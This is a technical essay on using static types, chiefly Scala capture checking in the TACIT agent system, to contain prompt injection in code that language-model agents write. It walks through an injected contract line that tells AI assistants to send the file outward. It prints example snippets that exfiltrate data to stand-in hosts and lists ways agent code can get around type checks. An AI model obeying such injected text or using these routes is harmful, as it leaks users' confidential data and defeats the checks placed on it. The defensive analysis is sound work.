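# Static type checking as a defence against prompt injection in code written by language models

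## How injected text turns into a program, and what a type checker sees of it

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model, in which an attacker writes text that the model treats as an instruction, against the wishes of the user or the company that operates the software. AI agents (programs in which a model pursues a task with tools such as email, files and web search) increasingly act by writing code. With static type checking, a compiler checks before a program runs that every operation in it applies to values of a permitted kind. The compiler might therefore refuse to let the agent's code run, even if an attacker has gained control over what the model writes.

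### Instructions and data in the same text

In a direct injection, the hostile text is in the user's prompt. The user may be the attacker, or may have pasted in text from an attacker's website without reading it closely. An injection is indirect if the agent reads the hostile text while working, for example in a web page, a file or an email. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023) introduced indirect injection and demonstrated it on Microsoft's Bing Chat, among other systems. Bing Chat could read whatever page the user had open in the Edge browser, and instructions on that page steered the model even when they were invisible to the user. An attacker can therefore inject instructions without access to the victim's system, by placing text where the model will read it.

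Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) describe the weakness in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*. The software joins the developer's prompt p and the outside data d into one string, and the model F computes F(p‖d). If p is a request to summarise a document, and d is a document with another request somewhere in the middle, the model receives one string containing two requests.

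Databases had a similar problem, SQL injection, which developers know how to prevent. An attacker types a fragment of SQL, the language of database queries, into a field on a web page, and the database runs it. Parameterised queries keep the query separate from the values that go into it, so the database engine never interprets a value as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models cannot be fixed this way because they have no built-in separation between instructions and data. A model only predicts the next token, which is a word or piece of a word, from the tokens before it. David C grants that putting markers around the data or training the model to prioritise the user's instructions makes attacks harder. But these measures do not build the separation into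 the model, and he thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever eliminate the vulnerability completely.

An agent that took no instructions from what it reads would be of little use. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) points out that a tool's documentation is outside text, and that an agent has to change its behaviour in response to it in order to use the tool. The paper also describes a legitimate case in which an agent summarises a software issue, finds that it depends on another issue, and summarises both. A filter that recognised every instruction in every document would therefore still have to decide which of them the agent may follow.

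### From the contract to the program

In ReAct, the dominant design for agents, the model alternates between reasoning and single tool calls. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) contrasts this with agents that write snippets, short programs that can call several tools, loop over their results and branch on what they find. A ReAct agent may need forty calls to open forty contracts, but a snippet needs only one loop. An agent that first writes its plan as code also gives security analysts something to inspect before it acts. Christodorescu and colleagues observe that analysts normally have a fixed program to examine, whereas an agent makes up its behaviour as it goes along.

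Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise a supplier's contract. The supplier, or someone with access to the supplier's files, has added a line to an annex telling AI assistants to send the file to an outside address. A harmless snippet of code has already opened the contract and returned its text.

1. The text of the contract, including the hostile line, enters the model's context next to the user's request.
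2. The model computes its next output from everything in the context. If the injection works, it works here.
3. The output is a snippet.
4. The compiler checks the snippet. **This is the only step at which a type checker acts.**
5. If the snippet passes, the runtime executes it. Files open and messages leave.
6. The output of the snippet goes back into the model's context, along with any hostile text it carries, and the next round begins.

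A snippet from a successful injection might look like this:

```
val text = read("contract.txt")
send("archive@supplier.example", text)
summarise(text)
```

At step 4, an ordinary type checker confirms that `read` takes a file name and returns a string, that `send` takes two strings and has received two strings, and that `summarise` takes a string, so the program passes. The checker has no access to the user's request and has not processed the contract's text. If the user had asked the assistant to forward the contract to that address and then summarise it, the model could have written the same three lines, and the compiler would have accepted them for the same reasons.

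The main objection to type checking as a defence, which is correct but incomplete, is that the injection is over before the checker has anything to check. Hostile text acts on the model, and the checker examines only the program that the model then writes. It gives the same verdict on a given snippet whether an honest request or an attack produced it, so it can neither prevent an injection nor detect one.

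The people who build these systems do not dispute this. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system from the Swiss university EPFL that compiles an agent's snippets before running them, and states outright that TACIT does not keep hostile content from influencing the agent. Zhao and colleagues call such influence unavoidable once untrusted text has reached the prompt. Both groups want to limit what the influence can accomplish. It helps that the checker does not see the text, because no wording can make a compiler accept a program that breaks its rules. The objection would matter little if types could distinguish every harmful snippet from every legitimate one, but the three lines above show that ordinary types do not record enough to do so.

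### What types can record

A static type is a description that the compiler attaches to a value before the program runs. Since `text` has the type `String`, the compiler rejects `squareRoot(text)`. Zhao and colleagues point out that ordinary types govern the shape of an action but not its authority. A type system needs a few more concepts to describe authority.

An effect is any interaction between a computation and the world outside it. For example, `send(address, text)` has an effect because a message leaves the machine. A pure function has no effects and holds no capabilities, so `wordCount(text)`, if pure, returns a number and does nothing else. In many common languages, a function that only counts words has the same type as one that also uploads them.

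A privileged operation is an action with consequences outside the program, such as writing a file, sending a message or making a payment. A capability is a value that code must hold to perform a given privileged operation and cannot forge. For example, only code that has received the value `mailer` can call `mailer.send(address, text)`. TACIT also uses capture checking, a feature of the Scala language, to record in types which capabilities a value may use.

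Information-flow control limits where data may go after a program has read it, while read permissions only limit who may read it. For example, a rule might let a snippet read the contract but forbid it to put any part of it into an outgoing email.

All such guarantees depend on a trusted base of components that must work correctly. If a compiler bug let a snippet create its own `mailer`, the rule about capabilities would give no protection. For TACIT, Odersky and colleagues list the Scala compiler, the library that provides capabilities, the runtime and, where an operator uses one, a local model that processes secret text. They exclude the model that drives the agent and assume that it may cooperate fully with the attacker.

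That last decision is the main difference from defences that train the model to behave. Christodorescu and colleagues explain that if a model in the trusted base correctly refuses unauthorised access 99% of the time, attackers can search for the 1% it allows. Nor can anyone prove that a model will always enforce a policy. A compiler has bugs too, but developers can find and fix them, and whether it accepts a given program does not depend on how persuasive a contract is.

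### A model that reads and a model that acts

Another answer to the objection is to keep the hostile text away from the model that decides what to do. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using two models with an ordinary program, the controller, between them. The privileged model takes requests from the user and can call tools, while the quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools.

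In the contract example, the privileged model would request the file through the controller, which would store the text under a name, say `$VAR1`. The privileged model would then request a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller would pass the text to the quarantined model, store the reply as `$VAR2`, and report that the summary is ready. The privileged model would then instruct the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user. The privileged model never receives the text of the contract or the summary, and the quarantined model, which reads the hostile line, cannot send files.

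The solution has considerable drawbacks, and Willison himself called it "pretty bad". It complicates the software, and one careless feature that passes the text to the privileged model removes the protection. It also rules out any task in which the content should affect the next action. Jacob and colleagues give the example of a bug-fixing agent, which has to guess what is broken if the privileged model may not read the bug reports. Some designs go further and fix the whole plan before any model reads the data. *Twin Agent* (2026) describes this as a poor fit for long tasks such as software engineering, where an agent must keep adjusting its plan to the results. Willison allowed one exception, for replies that the controller can verify, such as a choice from a fixed set of categories. Jacob and colleagues build on a similar idea when they use data types to restrict what the privileged model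 reads.

The arrangement also leaves the user exposed. The quarantined model writes the summary, and the hostile line can shape what it writes.

### Four ways the contract can do harm

Return to an assistant with a single model that has read the whole contract. Suppose that the operator has handed out permissions with some care. The assistant's code may read and save files in the contracts folder, and it may run web searches, which help it to look up the companies that a contract mentions. It may not send email. An attacker who knows this can reword the line in the annex to suit, and the attack can then end in any of four ways:

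- The snippet uses a permission it does not have. It tries to email the contract to the outside address.
- The snippet leaks the text through a permitted channel. It runs a web search and puts the confidential prices from the contract into the query.
- The snippet misuses a permission it does have. It saves an altered version of the contract over the signed one. No secret leaves the company, and the snippet touches only the folder it may touch.
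- The model writes no harmful code at all and gives a misleading reply. The summary tells the user that the contract contains no penalty clause, and the user signs.

Greshake and colleagues listed misleading replies, in the form of manipulated summaries, among the threats in 2023, and they worried that users would trust an authoritative tone. Definitions of prompt injection differ on such cases. Jacob and colleagues include any input that makes the model depart from its task, but exclude inputs that merely feed it false information. Under this definition, a line that orders the model to conceal the penalty clause is an injection, but a contract with a false statement about penalties is not, although both may leave the user with the same wrong belief.

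These four outcomes will fare differently under the systems that follow.

### How researchers measure the damage

The most popular test of defences against prompt injection is *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), from ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs. It simulates four domains: a bank, a travel agency, the messaging service Slack, and a workspace with email, a calendar and cloud files. Each domain has tools that read or change its data. The original version contains 97 user tasks, such as paying the bill in a given file, and 27 injection tasks, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker. Within each domain, AgentDojo pairs every user task with every injection task. The bank's 16 user tasks and 9 injection tasks make 144 pairs, and the four domains together make 629.

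For each pair, AgentDojo plants the injection in data that the agent has to read for the user's task, such as the body of an email. After the run, ordinary code checks the agent's answer and the state of the simulated world, including whether money moved and to whom. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that works on the agent might also work on the judge.

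The benchmark measures utility and attack success rate. Utility is the share of the user's tasks that the agent completes correctly. Debenedetti and colleagues measure it both without an attack and under attack, where a run counts only if the injection caused no side effects. The attack success rate is the share of pairs of user task and attacker's goal in which the agent achieves the attacker's goal. Neither figure means much alone, since an agent that refuses all work would have an attack success rate of zero but also no utility. In the original experiments, the more capable models tended to be easier to attack. Debenedetti and colleagues suggest that this is because weak models often failed to carry out the attacker's task even after accepting the injected instructions.

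AgentDojo scores require careful interpretation. Debenedetti and colleagues' examples of attacker goals are actions, such as forwarding a security code or booking an expensive hotel. A dishonest summary would lower the utility score, if it affected the scores at all. The benchmark has also grown to over 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), so scores from different years may come from different versions of the test.

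More seriously, most researchers run AgentDojo with its stock injections, although Debenedetti and colleagues designed it so that others could add attacks adapted to a particular defence. *AutoDojo* (2026) supplies such attacks. Five defences had kept the stock attack's success rate close to zero on an agent running GPT-4o-mini, a small, older model. When AutoDojo adapted the injections, attacks succeeded again against four of the five. Some defences still worked, especially those that restrict the system around the model.

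The newest evidence on models that have to protect themselves comes from *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, by Kurakin, Karande and colleagues at Google DeepMind (2026). They ran an automated attacker against seven models in 100 synthetic scenarios, with the defences that normally surround Google's Gemini models switched off. The most robust model, Gemini 4 Argon, resisted in 66 scenarios, while the other six resisted in between 1 and 10. By contrast, attacks reused from a public contest among human attackers had succeeded against recent Gemini models less than 1% of the time.

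The test was harsh in two respects. First, the attacker could make up to 320 attempts per scenario, and Argon had still resisted every attack in 87 scenarios after the first 150 attempts. Second, the attacker's goal was an unrelated tool call that could be harmless, such as logging someone's blood pressure during a request about tutoring, so a model could not resist the attack by recognising a dangerous action. This second condition is fairly realistic for the contract, because sending a file is an everyday action that doesn't look dangerous unless one knows who asked for it.

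## Ordinary static types: well-typed code that still does harm

Many coding assistants write in languages with conventional static types, such as Java, TypeScript or Scala. Suppose a developer asks an assistant for a function that checks whether a settings file is valid. While working, the assistant reads the documentation of a third-party library, where an attacker has added a line telling AI assistants to send every file they handle to an outside address. The model obeys and writes this:

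```
def isValid(path: String): Boolean =
  val text = readFile(path)
  upload("https://collect.example", text)
  text.startsWith("version")
```

This function takes a string and returns true or false. Its type stays the same if the developer deletes the line with `upload`, and the compiler accepts both versions.

The compiler would reject the call to `upload` if the model had passed it a number instead of the text, but it would accept the call if the model had swapped the address and the text, since both are strings. Even a rejection may help the attacker. Coding tools often pass compiler errors back to the model so that it can repair its code, as *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) mentions, and these errors would help it repair an injected upload with a type error just as they would any other code.

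Well-typed code can do harm even in a language with a formal proof of type safety. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) defines a small formal language for agents and gives a machine-checked proof that a well-typed agent either returns a value of the expected type or stops with a well-defined error. In this language, a call to a model has the type Str → Str, meaning that it takes a string and returns a string, as tools also do. The theorem therefore holds both for a harmless tool and for one that emails its input to a stranger. Liu leaves types that record effects as a possible extension.

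### Code injection and prompt injection

Types do help against code injection, an attack with a similar name in which an attacker feeds hostile data to a finished program and the program treats part of the data as code. SQL injection is one example. In another, a visitor to a website that greets people by name enters a script as his name, and the page runs it. The programmer in these cases is honest but careless, and types are good at catching careless mistakes. In prompt injection, the hostile text reaches the model that writes the program, possibly before any program exists.

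Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic (2025), in *TypePilot*, tried to get models to use types to guard against careless handling of input. TypePilot calls a model three times. The first call writes a Scala program for the task, the second lists the program's vulnerabilities without writing any code, and the third rewrites the program, with instructions to fix those vulnerabilities using Scala's type system. The paper compares this method with a baseline, in which the model received only the task, and with "robust prompting", in which a single prompt asked for safe code and recommended the same features of the type system.

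They name six models but report detailed grades for three, all with open weights: Qwen2.5-Coder 32B, CodeLlama 70B and DeepSeek-Coder 33B. The tasks on input validation were small calculations, such as averaging a list of ages, and the researchers checked by hand whether the programs coped with negative ages, empty matrices and the like. The tasks on code injection were to greet a user in HTML, list comments in HTML, search for a file, ping a host and build a web address for a redirect. Added up over the three models, the grades come to:

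| | Baseline | Robust prompting | TypePilot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Input checks passed, of 45 | 19 | 23 | 35 |
| Programs fully safe against code injection, of 15 | 1 | 6 | 14 |

The improvement is large, but the test was small. One of the 14 safe programs also failed the separate check for compiling and working correctly. It is hard to say how much of the improvement is due to types, because only TypePilot had a model review the finished code for vulnerabilities before rewriting it.

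The file search shows what types contribute. In TypePilot's version, the function `findFile` accepts only a value of type `ValidFilename`, and the program creates such values with a function that first tests the name against a pattern of letters, digits and a few punctuation marks. The test happens when the program runs. The compiler's job is to reject any code that passes an untested string to `findFile`. (The baseline version in the paper already handed the name to the search program as a separate argument, with no shell to interpret it, so there was less danger to remove than the paper suggests.)

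This works only if there is no other way to make a `ValidFilename`. But the class in the paper's listing has a public constructor, so `new Filename("../../secret")` compiles and skips the test. An honest programmer would probably never write that, but a model following an attacker's instructions might. It would not need to, since `findFile` launches an outside program, and its type would be the same if that program uploaded files. TypePilot protects a finished program from a malicious filename, but it assumes that the model writing the program is following the user's instructions, not an attacker's, and that model writes both the types and the code that has to satisfy them.

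An attacker can also combine the two attacks, using hostile text to lead a model to write a program that is open to code injection later. In *Hidden in the Comments*, Munir, Quinzan and Roberts (2026) gave ten open-weight models (3 to 13 billion parameters) 700 small Python web applications to complete. Each application contained a comment that asked for something insecure, such as running whatever system command a visitor names. Depending on the model, 77.4% to 92.3% of the completed programs had a weakness of at least medium severity, compared with 1.7% to 5.1% on ordinary coding tasks.

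These figures probably overstate the danger. The ordinary tasks were different programs rather than the same programs with the comment removed. The prompt also told the models to complete every part marked with such a comment, so a model that obeyed the comment was doing what the user had asked. Munir and colleagues acknowledge that they measured compliance, not whether a complete attack succeeded. Still, scanning the code afterwards was a weak remedy, because the best scanner missed about a third of the vulnerable programs. A conventional type checker would not have done better on the system command, because it treats a command's name like any other string. It could have helped if someone other than the model had written the types, for example by providing a function that runs only commands from a fixed list.

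### Ways out of the type system

Suppose the operator of the coding assistant supplies a small library that can only read and change the project's settings, and instructs the model to use only that library. In a conventional language, the model's code can still reach files and the network with one import from the standard library. The operator could reject programs with forbidden imports, but conventional languages also have features that let code get around its own types.

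A cast asserts that a value has a certain type, and the compiler largely accepts this without checking. TypeScript also lets a programmer suppress the type error on a line by putting a special comment above it. Reflection lets a running program look up classes and functions by name. Since the name is an ordinary string, a program can assemble it from harmless-looking pieces, and neither the type checker nor a search for forbidden names will find it. In Rust, code in an `unsafe` block can write to arbitrary memory addresses, including those of values that the types are supposed to protect. The simplest way around the type checker is to start another process. The compiler treats `run("curl ...")` as a function applied to a string, although the string may be a complete program in another language.

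Odersky and colleagues describe casts and reflection as necessary in general programming, but note that they can make a program "forget" capabilities, so that a type no longer lists everything a value may use. They conclude that code from an untrusted agent must do without these features. Even Haskell, known for its strict types, has `unsafePerformIO`, which lets a computation perform an effect that its type doesn't show. TACIT and ELBA, which later sections describe, use Scala's safe mode and Safe Haskell respectively, restricted versions of the two languages that exclude such features.

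Some code runs before the compiler has finished checking types. Cargo, the standard build tool for Rust, compiles and runs a package's build script before it compiles the package itself, normally with all the permissions of the user who started it. Macros (code that generates other code) also run during compilation in Rust and Scala. An assistant that can add a build script to a project can therefore upload the settings file when the developer runs a type check, even if the compiler then rejects the program.

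### When the model can change the rules

A coding assistant usually edits a whole project, including the parts that determine what the compiler will accept. If `findFile` requires a `ValidFilename`, the model can change the signature to accept any `String`. It can add a dependency whose functions upload files internally but have types that don't show it. In TypeScript, it can turn off the strict checks in the project's settings file. After any of these changes, the developer sees the same successful build as before.

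Sternfeld and colleagues found a case of this that involved no attacker. Before building TypePilot, they asked models to write programs for Stainless, a tool for proving that Scala code meets stated conditions. None of the models could do this reliably. One program for computing factorials compiled, but the model had marked functions in it with `@library`. This annotation makes Stainless skip functions that are supposed to have been verified elsewhere, and nobody had verified these. A user who looked only at the result would have believed that the program was proven correct. The model need not have meant to deceive anyone, since the annotation was part of the language it had been asked to write.

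The operator can fix this by keeping the signatures, dependency list and compiler settings where the model cannot write to them, and compiling the model's code against those copies. This is easy for a short snippet but awkward for a coding assistant, whose legitimate work includes changing signatures and adding dependencies.

### Forcing a model to write well-typed code

Enforcing type rules as the model writes code may seem safer, because the model then cannot produce an ill-typed program. Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) do this for part of TypeScript in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*.

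Each time the model samples a token, Mündler and colleagues' system checks whether the text so far, including that token, can be extended into a well-typed program. If it cannot, the system sets the token's probability to zero and samples again. An ordinary type checker cannot perform this check because it works only on complete programs. Mündler and colleagues therefore built an automaton that reads the program character by character and tracks which variables exist and their types.

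Suppose the model has written `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number and `parseInt` requires a string. CodeLlama 34B's own continuation was `, 10)`, which does not compile. The system searches for operations that produce a string from a number, finds `.toString()`, and lets the model continue with that.

Mündler and colleagues tried this with six open-weight models on HumanEval and MBPP, two standard collections of programming exercises. When the models wrote programs from a description or translated them from Python, the constraint reduced compiler errors by 75.3% on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP. The number of programs that passed their tests rose much less, by a relative average of 3.5% for those written from a description. Even that figure may overstate the gain, because the researchers kept every program that compiled without help and applied the constraint only to new attempts at those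 that had failed to compile. They did this because the system did not support all of TypeScript.

Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, repeated the experiment with the constraint on throughout. Unconstrained models wrote more correct programs than constrained ones in all but two of 24 combinations of model, exercises and sampling temperature, and in those two the difference was not significant. Biagiola and colleagues attribute this to features that the constraint doesn't support, including imports, user-defined types and calls to functions defined later in the program. In one exercise, a model began a call to `isPalindrome`, which it would normally have defined later. The constraint blocked the name partway through, and the model wrote `isNaN` instead, a built-in test for whether a value is not a number. The resulting program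 was well typed but gave wrong answers.

Better coverage of the language could solve that problem, but it would not make the method a defence against injection. The function `isValid` is well-typed even with its upload, so every prefix of it can be completed into a well-typed program, and the constraint would never block it. If the model made a type error in the call to `upload`, the constraint would steer it towards a version that compiles. An operator could prevent the call by leaving `upload` out of the functions available to the model, but the protection would then come from the operator's choice of functions, which a check on the finished program could also enforce.

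### What the type checker would need

Type checking can help against prompt injection only if the types record effects. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives the example of a calculator whose code is written by a language model. A hostile user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. In Haskell, any program that runs a system command has the marker `IO` in its type. The calculator must return a plain `Int`, so the compiler rejects the program before it can delete anything.

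The types must also distinguish between effects. The function `isValid` has to read a file, so in Haskell its type would contain `IO` with or without the upload. To reject only the version with the upload, the operator needs a narrower type that allows reading settings but not network access.

Secondly, code must have no way around the checks. Odersky and colleagues divide this into two requirements: code must be unable to forge a capability or hide that it needs one, and capabilities must govern every effect that matters for safety, except those the runtime can contain. *ETAS* (2026), which presents an agent language whose types include effects, proves its guarantees under a similar assumption called complete mediation. This means that every operation on the outside world passes through the checked interface, so a single unguarded route to a shell would violate it.

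Finally, the model must not be able to change the interface against which the compiler checks its code. In Zhou and colleagues' design, the developer's program fixes the type that the model's code must have. If that code calls a model to write more code, the same restrictions or stricter ones apply to the result. The guarantee also holds only if the developer's own code, including the part that handles retries, is written in the same typed language.

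Even then, a person has to decide what the interface permits. If the developer's project legitimately needs to upload files and the operator provides a function that sends any string to any address, the injected version of `isValid` will meet all of these conditions and compile.

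## TACIT: Scala types that record what code may do

TACIT, short for Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types, tries to meet these conditions with Scala 3. Odersky and colleagues built it as a server that existing agents such as Claude Code or GitHub Copilot can connect to. The agent can be written in any language, as long as it writes its actions as Scala snippets.

### From snippet to result

TACIT connects to the agent through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for offering tools to agents. The agent calls TACIT as a tool and passes it a snippet of Scala code. The compiler checks each snippet in safe mode, a restricted version of the language, with capture checking switched on. If the compiler finds an error, the snippet doesn't run, and the error message goes back to the model, which can correct the snippet and try again. If the snippet compiles, a Scala interpreter on the user's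 machine runs it, and the output goes back into the model's context.

The snippet can reach files, the network, other programs and other models only through a library of capabilities. The operator supplies this library as a compiled file when the server starts, so the model can't loosen a signature the way a coding assistant can in an ordinary project. The extra check adds little time. A typical snippet compiles in under a second, and *What's in the Box* (2025), which describes the capture checker, reports that the check took less than 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

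Odersky and colleagues treat the cloud model, the agent's own code and settings, and everything the agent reads as untrusted. They want to stop a hostile or misled model from leaking secret data, including into its own conversation, which the model's provider can see. They also want to stop untrusted text from steering the agent into harmful actions. They claim that TACIT does not stop such text from influencing the model but "prevents the influence from translating into capability-violating actions". Even an attacker who controls the model completely still has to get a code snippet past the compiler.

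They then make the stronger claim that any injection that does real harm must either send private data to an unauthorised destination or trigger a capability that the agent was not given. This is too strong, because an injection could do neither and still cause real harm by overwriting the signed contract in a folder where the agent may write, or by producing a false summary.

### Capture sets

In Scala, a capability is an ordinary value, such as an open file. Scala's reference page *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives the example of a logger `lg` that writes messages to a file `out` and has the type `Logger^{out}`. `Logger` describes the kind of value, as in any typed language, and `{out}` is the capture set.

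In general, `T^{c1, ..., cn}` is the type of values of kind `T` that may use the capabilities c1 to cn and no others. A value may use fewer capabilities than its type lists, but never more. A plain `T` has an empty capture set, which makes it pure (unless `T` is itself a kind of capability), and `T^` allows any capability at all. Functions have their own notation:

| Type | What the function may use |
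|---|---|
| `A -> B` | no capabilities (a pure function) |
| `A ->{net} B` | only the capability `net` |
| `A => B` | any capability |

The compiler works out a function's capture set from its body. If `net` gives access to the network, a function that takes a string, looks it up through `net` and returns the answer has the type `String ->{net} String`.

Types with smaller capture sets are smaller types. If the set C is contained in the set D, then `T^C <: T^D`, where `<:` means that a value of the type on the left can go wherever the program expects the type on the right. For a type `A` and two capabilities `net` and `out`, this gives:

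```
A  <:  A^{net}  <:  A^{net, out}  <:  A^
```

A pure function can therefore stand in for one that may use the network, but not the reverse. The compiler also tracks capabilities held inside other values. The logger `lg` counts as a capability itself, and its type lists `out`, so the compiler infers that any function holding `lg` can reach the file.

One agent in Odersky and colleagues' tests broke this rule with harmless code. It wrote a helper function to print the first five lines of a file, and declared the function's parameter as `FileEntry`, the library's type for a file handle. Without a `^`, that is a pure type. The agent passed the function a handle of type `FileEntry^{contextual$1}`, where `contextual$1` is the compiler's own name for the permission to use the file system. The compiler doesn't allow that permission to be dropped from the type, so it rejected the program. Adding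 a `^` after `FileEntry` should fix the error, but the model then spends effort correcting harmless code.

### Two programs that the compiler rejects

To open files, a snippet calls `requestFileSystem` with a folder and a block of code. The function gives the block a `FileSystem` capability for that folder, runs the block and returns its result. Suppose that a snippet tries to keep a file handle for later:

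```
val handle = requestFileSystem("contracts") {
  access("contracts/supplier.txt")
}
handle.read()
```

The handle's type has the block's `FileSystem` capability in its capture set. In the signature of `requestFileSystem`, the result type `T` can be any type that is valid outside the block, where that capability does not exist. No such type fits the handle, so the compiler rejects the snippet. It would also reject a snippet that returned a function that opens the file later, or that stored the handle in a variable outside the block. An agent in the benchmark tried to return a list of file handles from its block and failed for this reason.

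An attacker who controls the next snippet can request file access again by calling `requestFileSystem`, because the permission this call requires, `IOCapability`, is available to all code at the top level of a snippet. Scoped capabilities stop code from keeping a permission after its block ends, and they make a program easier to read, since file access happens only inside a marked block. But they do not determine which folders the agent may open.

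The other rejection does more to stop an attack. TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`. The wrapper has a method `reveal` that returns the content, but only to code that holds a capability called `CanAccess`, which the agent never receives. The agent can still work on the content through the method `map`, which applies a function to it and wraps the result again. The function has to be of type `T -> U`, with the arrow for pure functions. In one test, an agent tried to print an access key for GitHub from inside `map`:

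```
githubKey.map { key =>
  println(s"GitHub API Key: $key")
}
```

The compiler answered with a type error:

```
Found:    (key: String) ->{x$1} Unit
Required: String -> Unit
```

The compiler also reported that the capability `x$1`, which is the permission to print, "cannot flow into capture set {}". Printing counts as an effect in TACIT because whatever a snippet prints goes back to the cloud model. Another agent tried to write secret text to a file from inside `map`, and the compiler found `outFile`, the file handle, in the function's capture set.

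A more careful attacker might avoid the existing handles and open a new file or network connection inside `map`. That fails because the request functions need `IOCapability`, which a pure function can't hold. The attacker might also have the function copy the secret into an ordinary variable, `copy`, and print it afterwards. That also fails because Scala treats mutable variables as capabilities, so a function that writes to `copy` has `copy` in its capture set and isn't pure.

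### The supplier's contract inside the wrapper

If the operator marks the contracts folder as classified, an honest agent can summarise the contract without reading it:

```
requestFileSystem("contracts") {
  val contract = readClassified("contracts/supplier.txt")
  val summary = chat(contract.map(t => s"Summarise this:\n$t"))
  println(summary)
}
```

The function `chat` sends the text to a second model, which the operator trusts with secrets and which normally runs locally. Its answer comes back inside `Classified`. This is Willison's two-model arrangement with a type in place of his controller. The type keeps the untrusted model from seeing the text, and `chat` gives the second model no tools.

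The user can read the summary because TACIT has two output channels. The normal channel goes to the agent, and from there into the cloud model's context, while the secure channel goes only to the user. `println` writes the same text to both channels for ordinary values, but for a classified value it shows the content only to the user and sends `Classified(****)` to the agent.

An agent can work in a session, where each new snippet can use names defined in earlier ones and the compiler checks it against everything already in the session. A file handle from an earlier turn no longer works because its block has ended, but the variable `contract` remains available, still in its wrapper. Odersky and colleagues present this as an advantage over systems that label sensitive data while a program runs. Those labels disappear once the data enters a model's conversation as plain text, whereas TACIT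 never lets classified text enter the agent's conversation.

The hostile line in the annex therefore never reaches the agent's model either. The attacker could instead plant the instructions on a web page that the agent finds while looking up the supplier. The injected snippet that tries to email the contract to the outside address does not compile, because the library has no function for sending email. If the snippet instead uses `httpPost` to send the text to a web address, it does not compile either, because `httpPost` takes a `String` and the contract is a `Classified[String]`.

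The injected snippet that leaks the prices through a web search looks like this, with `prices` standing for some code that picks them out of the text:

```
requestNetwork(Set("search.example")) {
  contract.map { t =>
    httpGet("https://search.example/?q=" + prices(t))
  }
}
```

A list of permitted actions would allow this code, because the agent may use the search engine and process the contract. The compiler rejects the code because the function inside `map` uses the network capability. Odersky and colleagues say that sandboxes, which confine a program to certain files and addresses, have the same limitation as a list of permitted actions. If a sandbox lets an agent read a private file and call a cloud model, it won't stop the agent from sending the file to the model.

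This protection depends on the wrapper. A plain `String` has an empty capture set wherever it came from, so if the operator had not marked the folder as classified, the search containing the prices would type-check. TACIT marks some locations as classified by default, including `.ssh`, `.env` and `.aws`, where developers tend to keep keys and passwords, but it does not do this for a folder of contracts.

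### Three properties and six restrictions

The guarantee of `Classified` holds only if the agent's programming language has three properties, which Odersky and colleagues call capability safety, capability completeness and local purity. Capability safety means that code can't forge or hide capabilities, so the agent can't make its own `CanAccess`. Capability completeness means that capabilities govern every effect that matters for safety, so the agent can't read the contract by a route that bypasses the wrapper. Local purity means that the types can limit a particular piece of code to a given set of capabilities, or to none, while the rest of the snippet may still read files and search the web.

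Full Scala has the same ways around its types as other conventional languages. Safe mode removes these with six restrictions, which Scala's *Safe Mode*, another page of the reference documentation, also lists:

| Restriction | What an agent could otherwise do |
|---|---|
| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | Assert that a function is pure although it holds a network capability |
| Nothing from the module `caps.unsafe` | Mark a variable so that the checker ignores it, and copy a secret there |
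| No `@unchecked` annotations | Tell the compiler to skip a check |
| No run-time reflection | Find and call a function by its name, so that its effects appear in no type |
| Capture checking always on, including for changes to variables | Write code whose types don't mention capabilities at all |
| Only those global objects and functions that are safe themselves | Call a library function that sends data without showing it in its type |

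The last restriction has exceptions. The compiler has a built-in list of standard library parts that it assumes are safe. The list includes most of Scala's own basic library but not the ordinary print functions, so TACIT supplies its own `println`. Other library authors can compile their code in safe mode or mark a module with `@assumeSafe`, which lets agents use it even though it contains forbidden features. The author of a marked module has to make sure by other means that it is harmless. The documentation's first example is a cache that stores the results of earlier calls. It changes a variable that the checker doesn't track, but callers can't tell, because the cache returns what the original function would have returned.

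The second example, a function that asks the user for confirmation before sending an email, is more worrying. It carries the same annotation, but nothing in its type shows that it sends anything, at least in the page's short outline. A snippet could then apparently call it inside `Classified.map`, and only the user's refusal would stop the contract from being sent to the outside address. The operator could avoid this by making the permission to send mail a capability.

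Safe mode also leaves exceptions out of the types. An exception is an error that can stop a program, and it carries a message that could contain the contract. The designers found it impractical to require a capability for every exception, because almost any line of code can fail, for example by dividing by zero or running out of memory. Instead, TACIT catches exceptions while the program runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap in `Classified` like any other secret. Scala 3 implements early returns and similar jumps as exceptions, so the same mechanism covers them.

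### What TACIT checks only at run time

Paths, web addresses and command names are all strings, and the compiler does not check what a string will contain. It can confirm that a snippet opens files only inside a `requestFileSystem` block, but TACIT checks at run time whether the path lies in the permitted folder. If it doesn't, the snippet stops with a `SecurityException`. At run time, the library also checks hosts in `requestNetwork`, commands in `requestExecPermission`, and whether a file belongs to a classified folder.

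This matters because the snippet writes its own permissions. In the search example above, the model chose the string `search.example`, and a model under an attacker's control can choose another. Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's README from October 2026, describes outer limits that the operator can set. By default, folder access is limited to the directory in which the server started. Hosts have no default outer limit, so only the list in the snippet applies. The settings in lampepfl's *TACIT*, the README of March 2026, include no outer limit for hosts.

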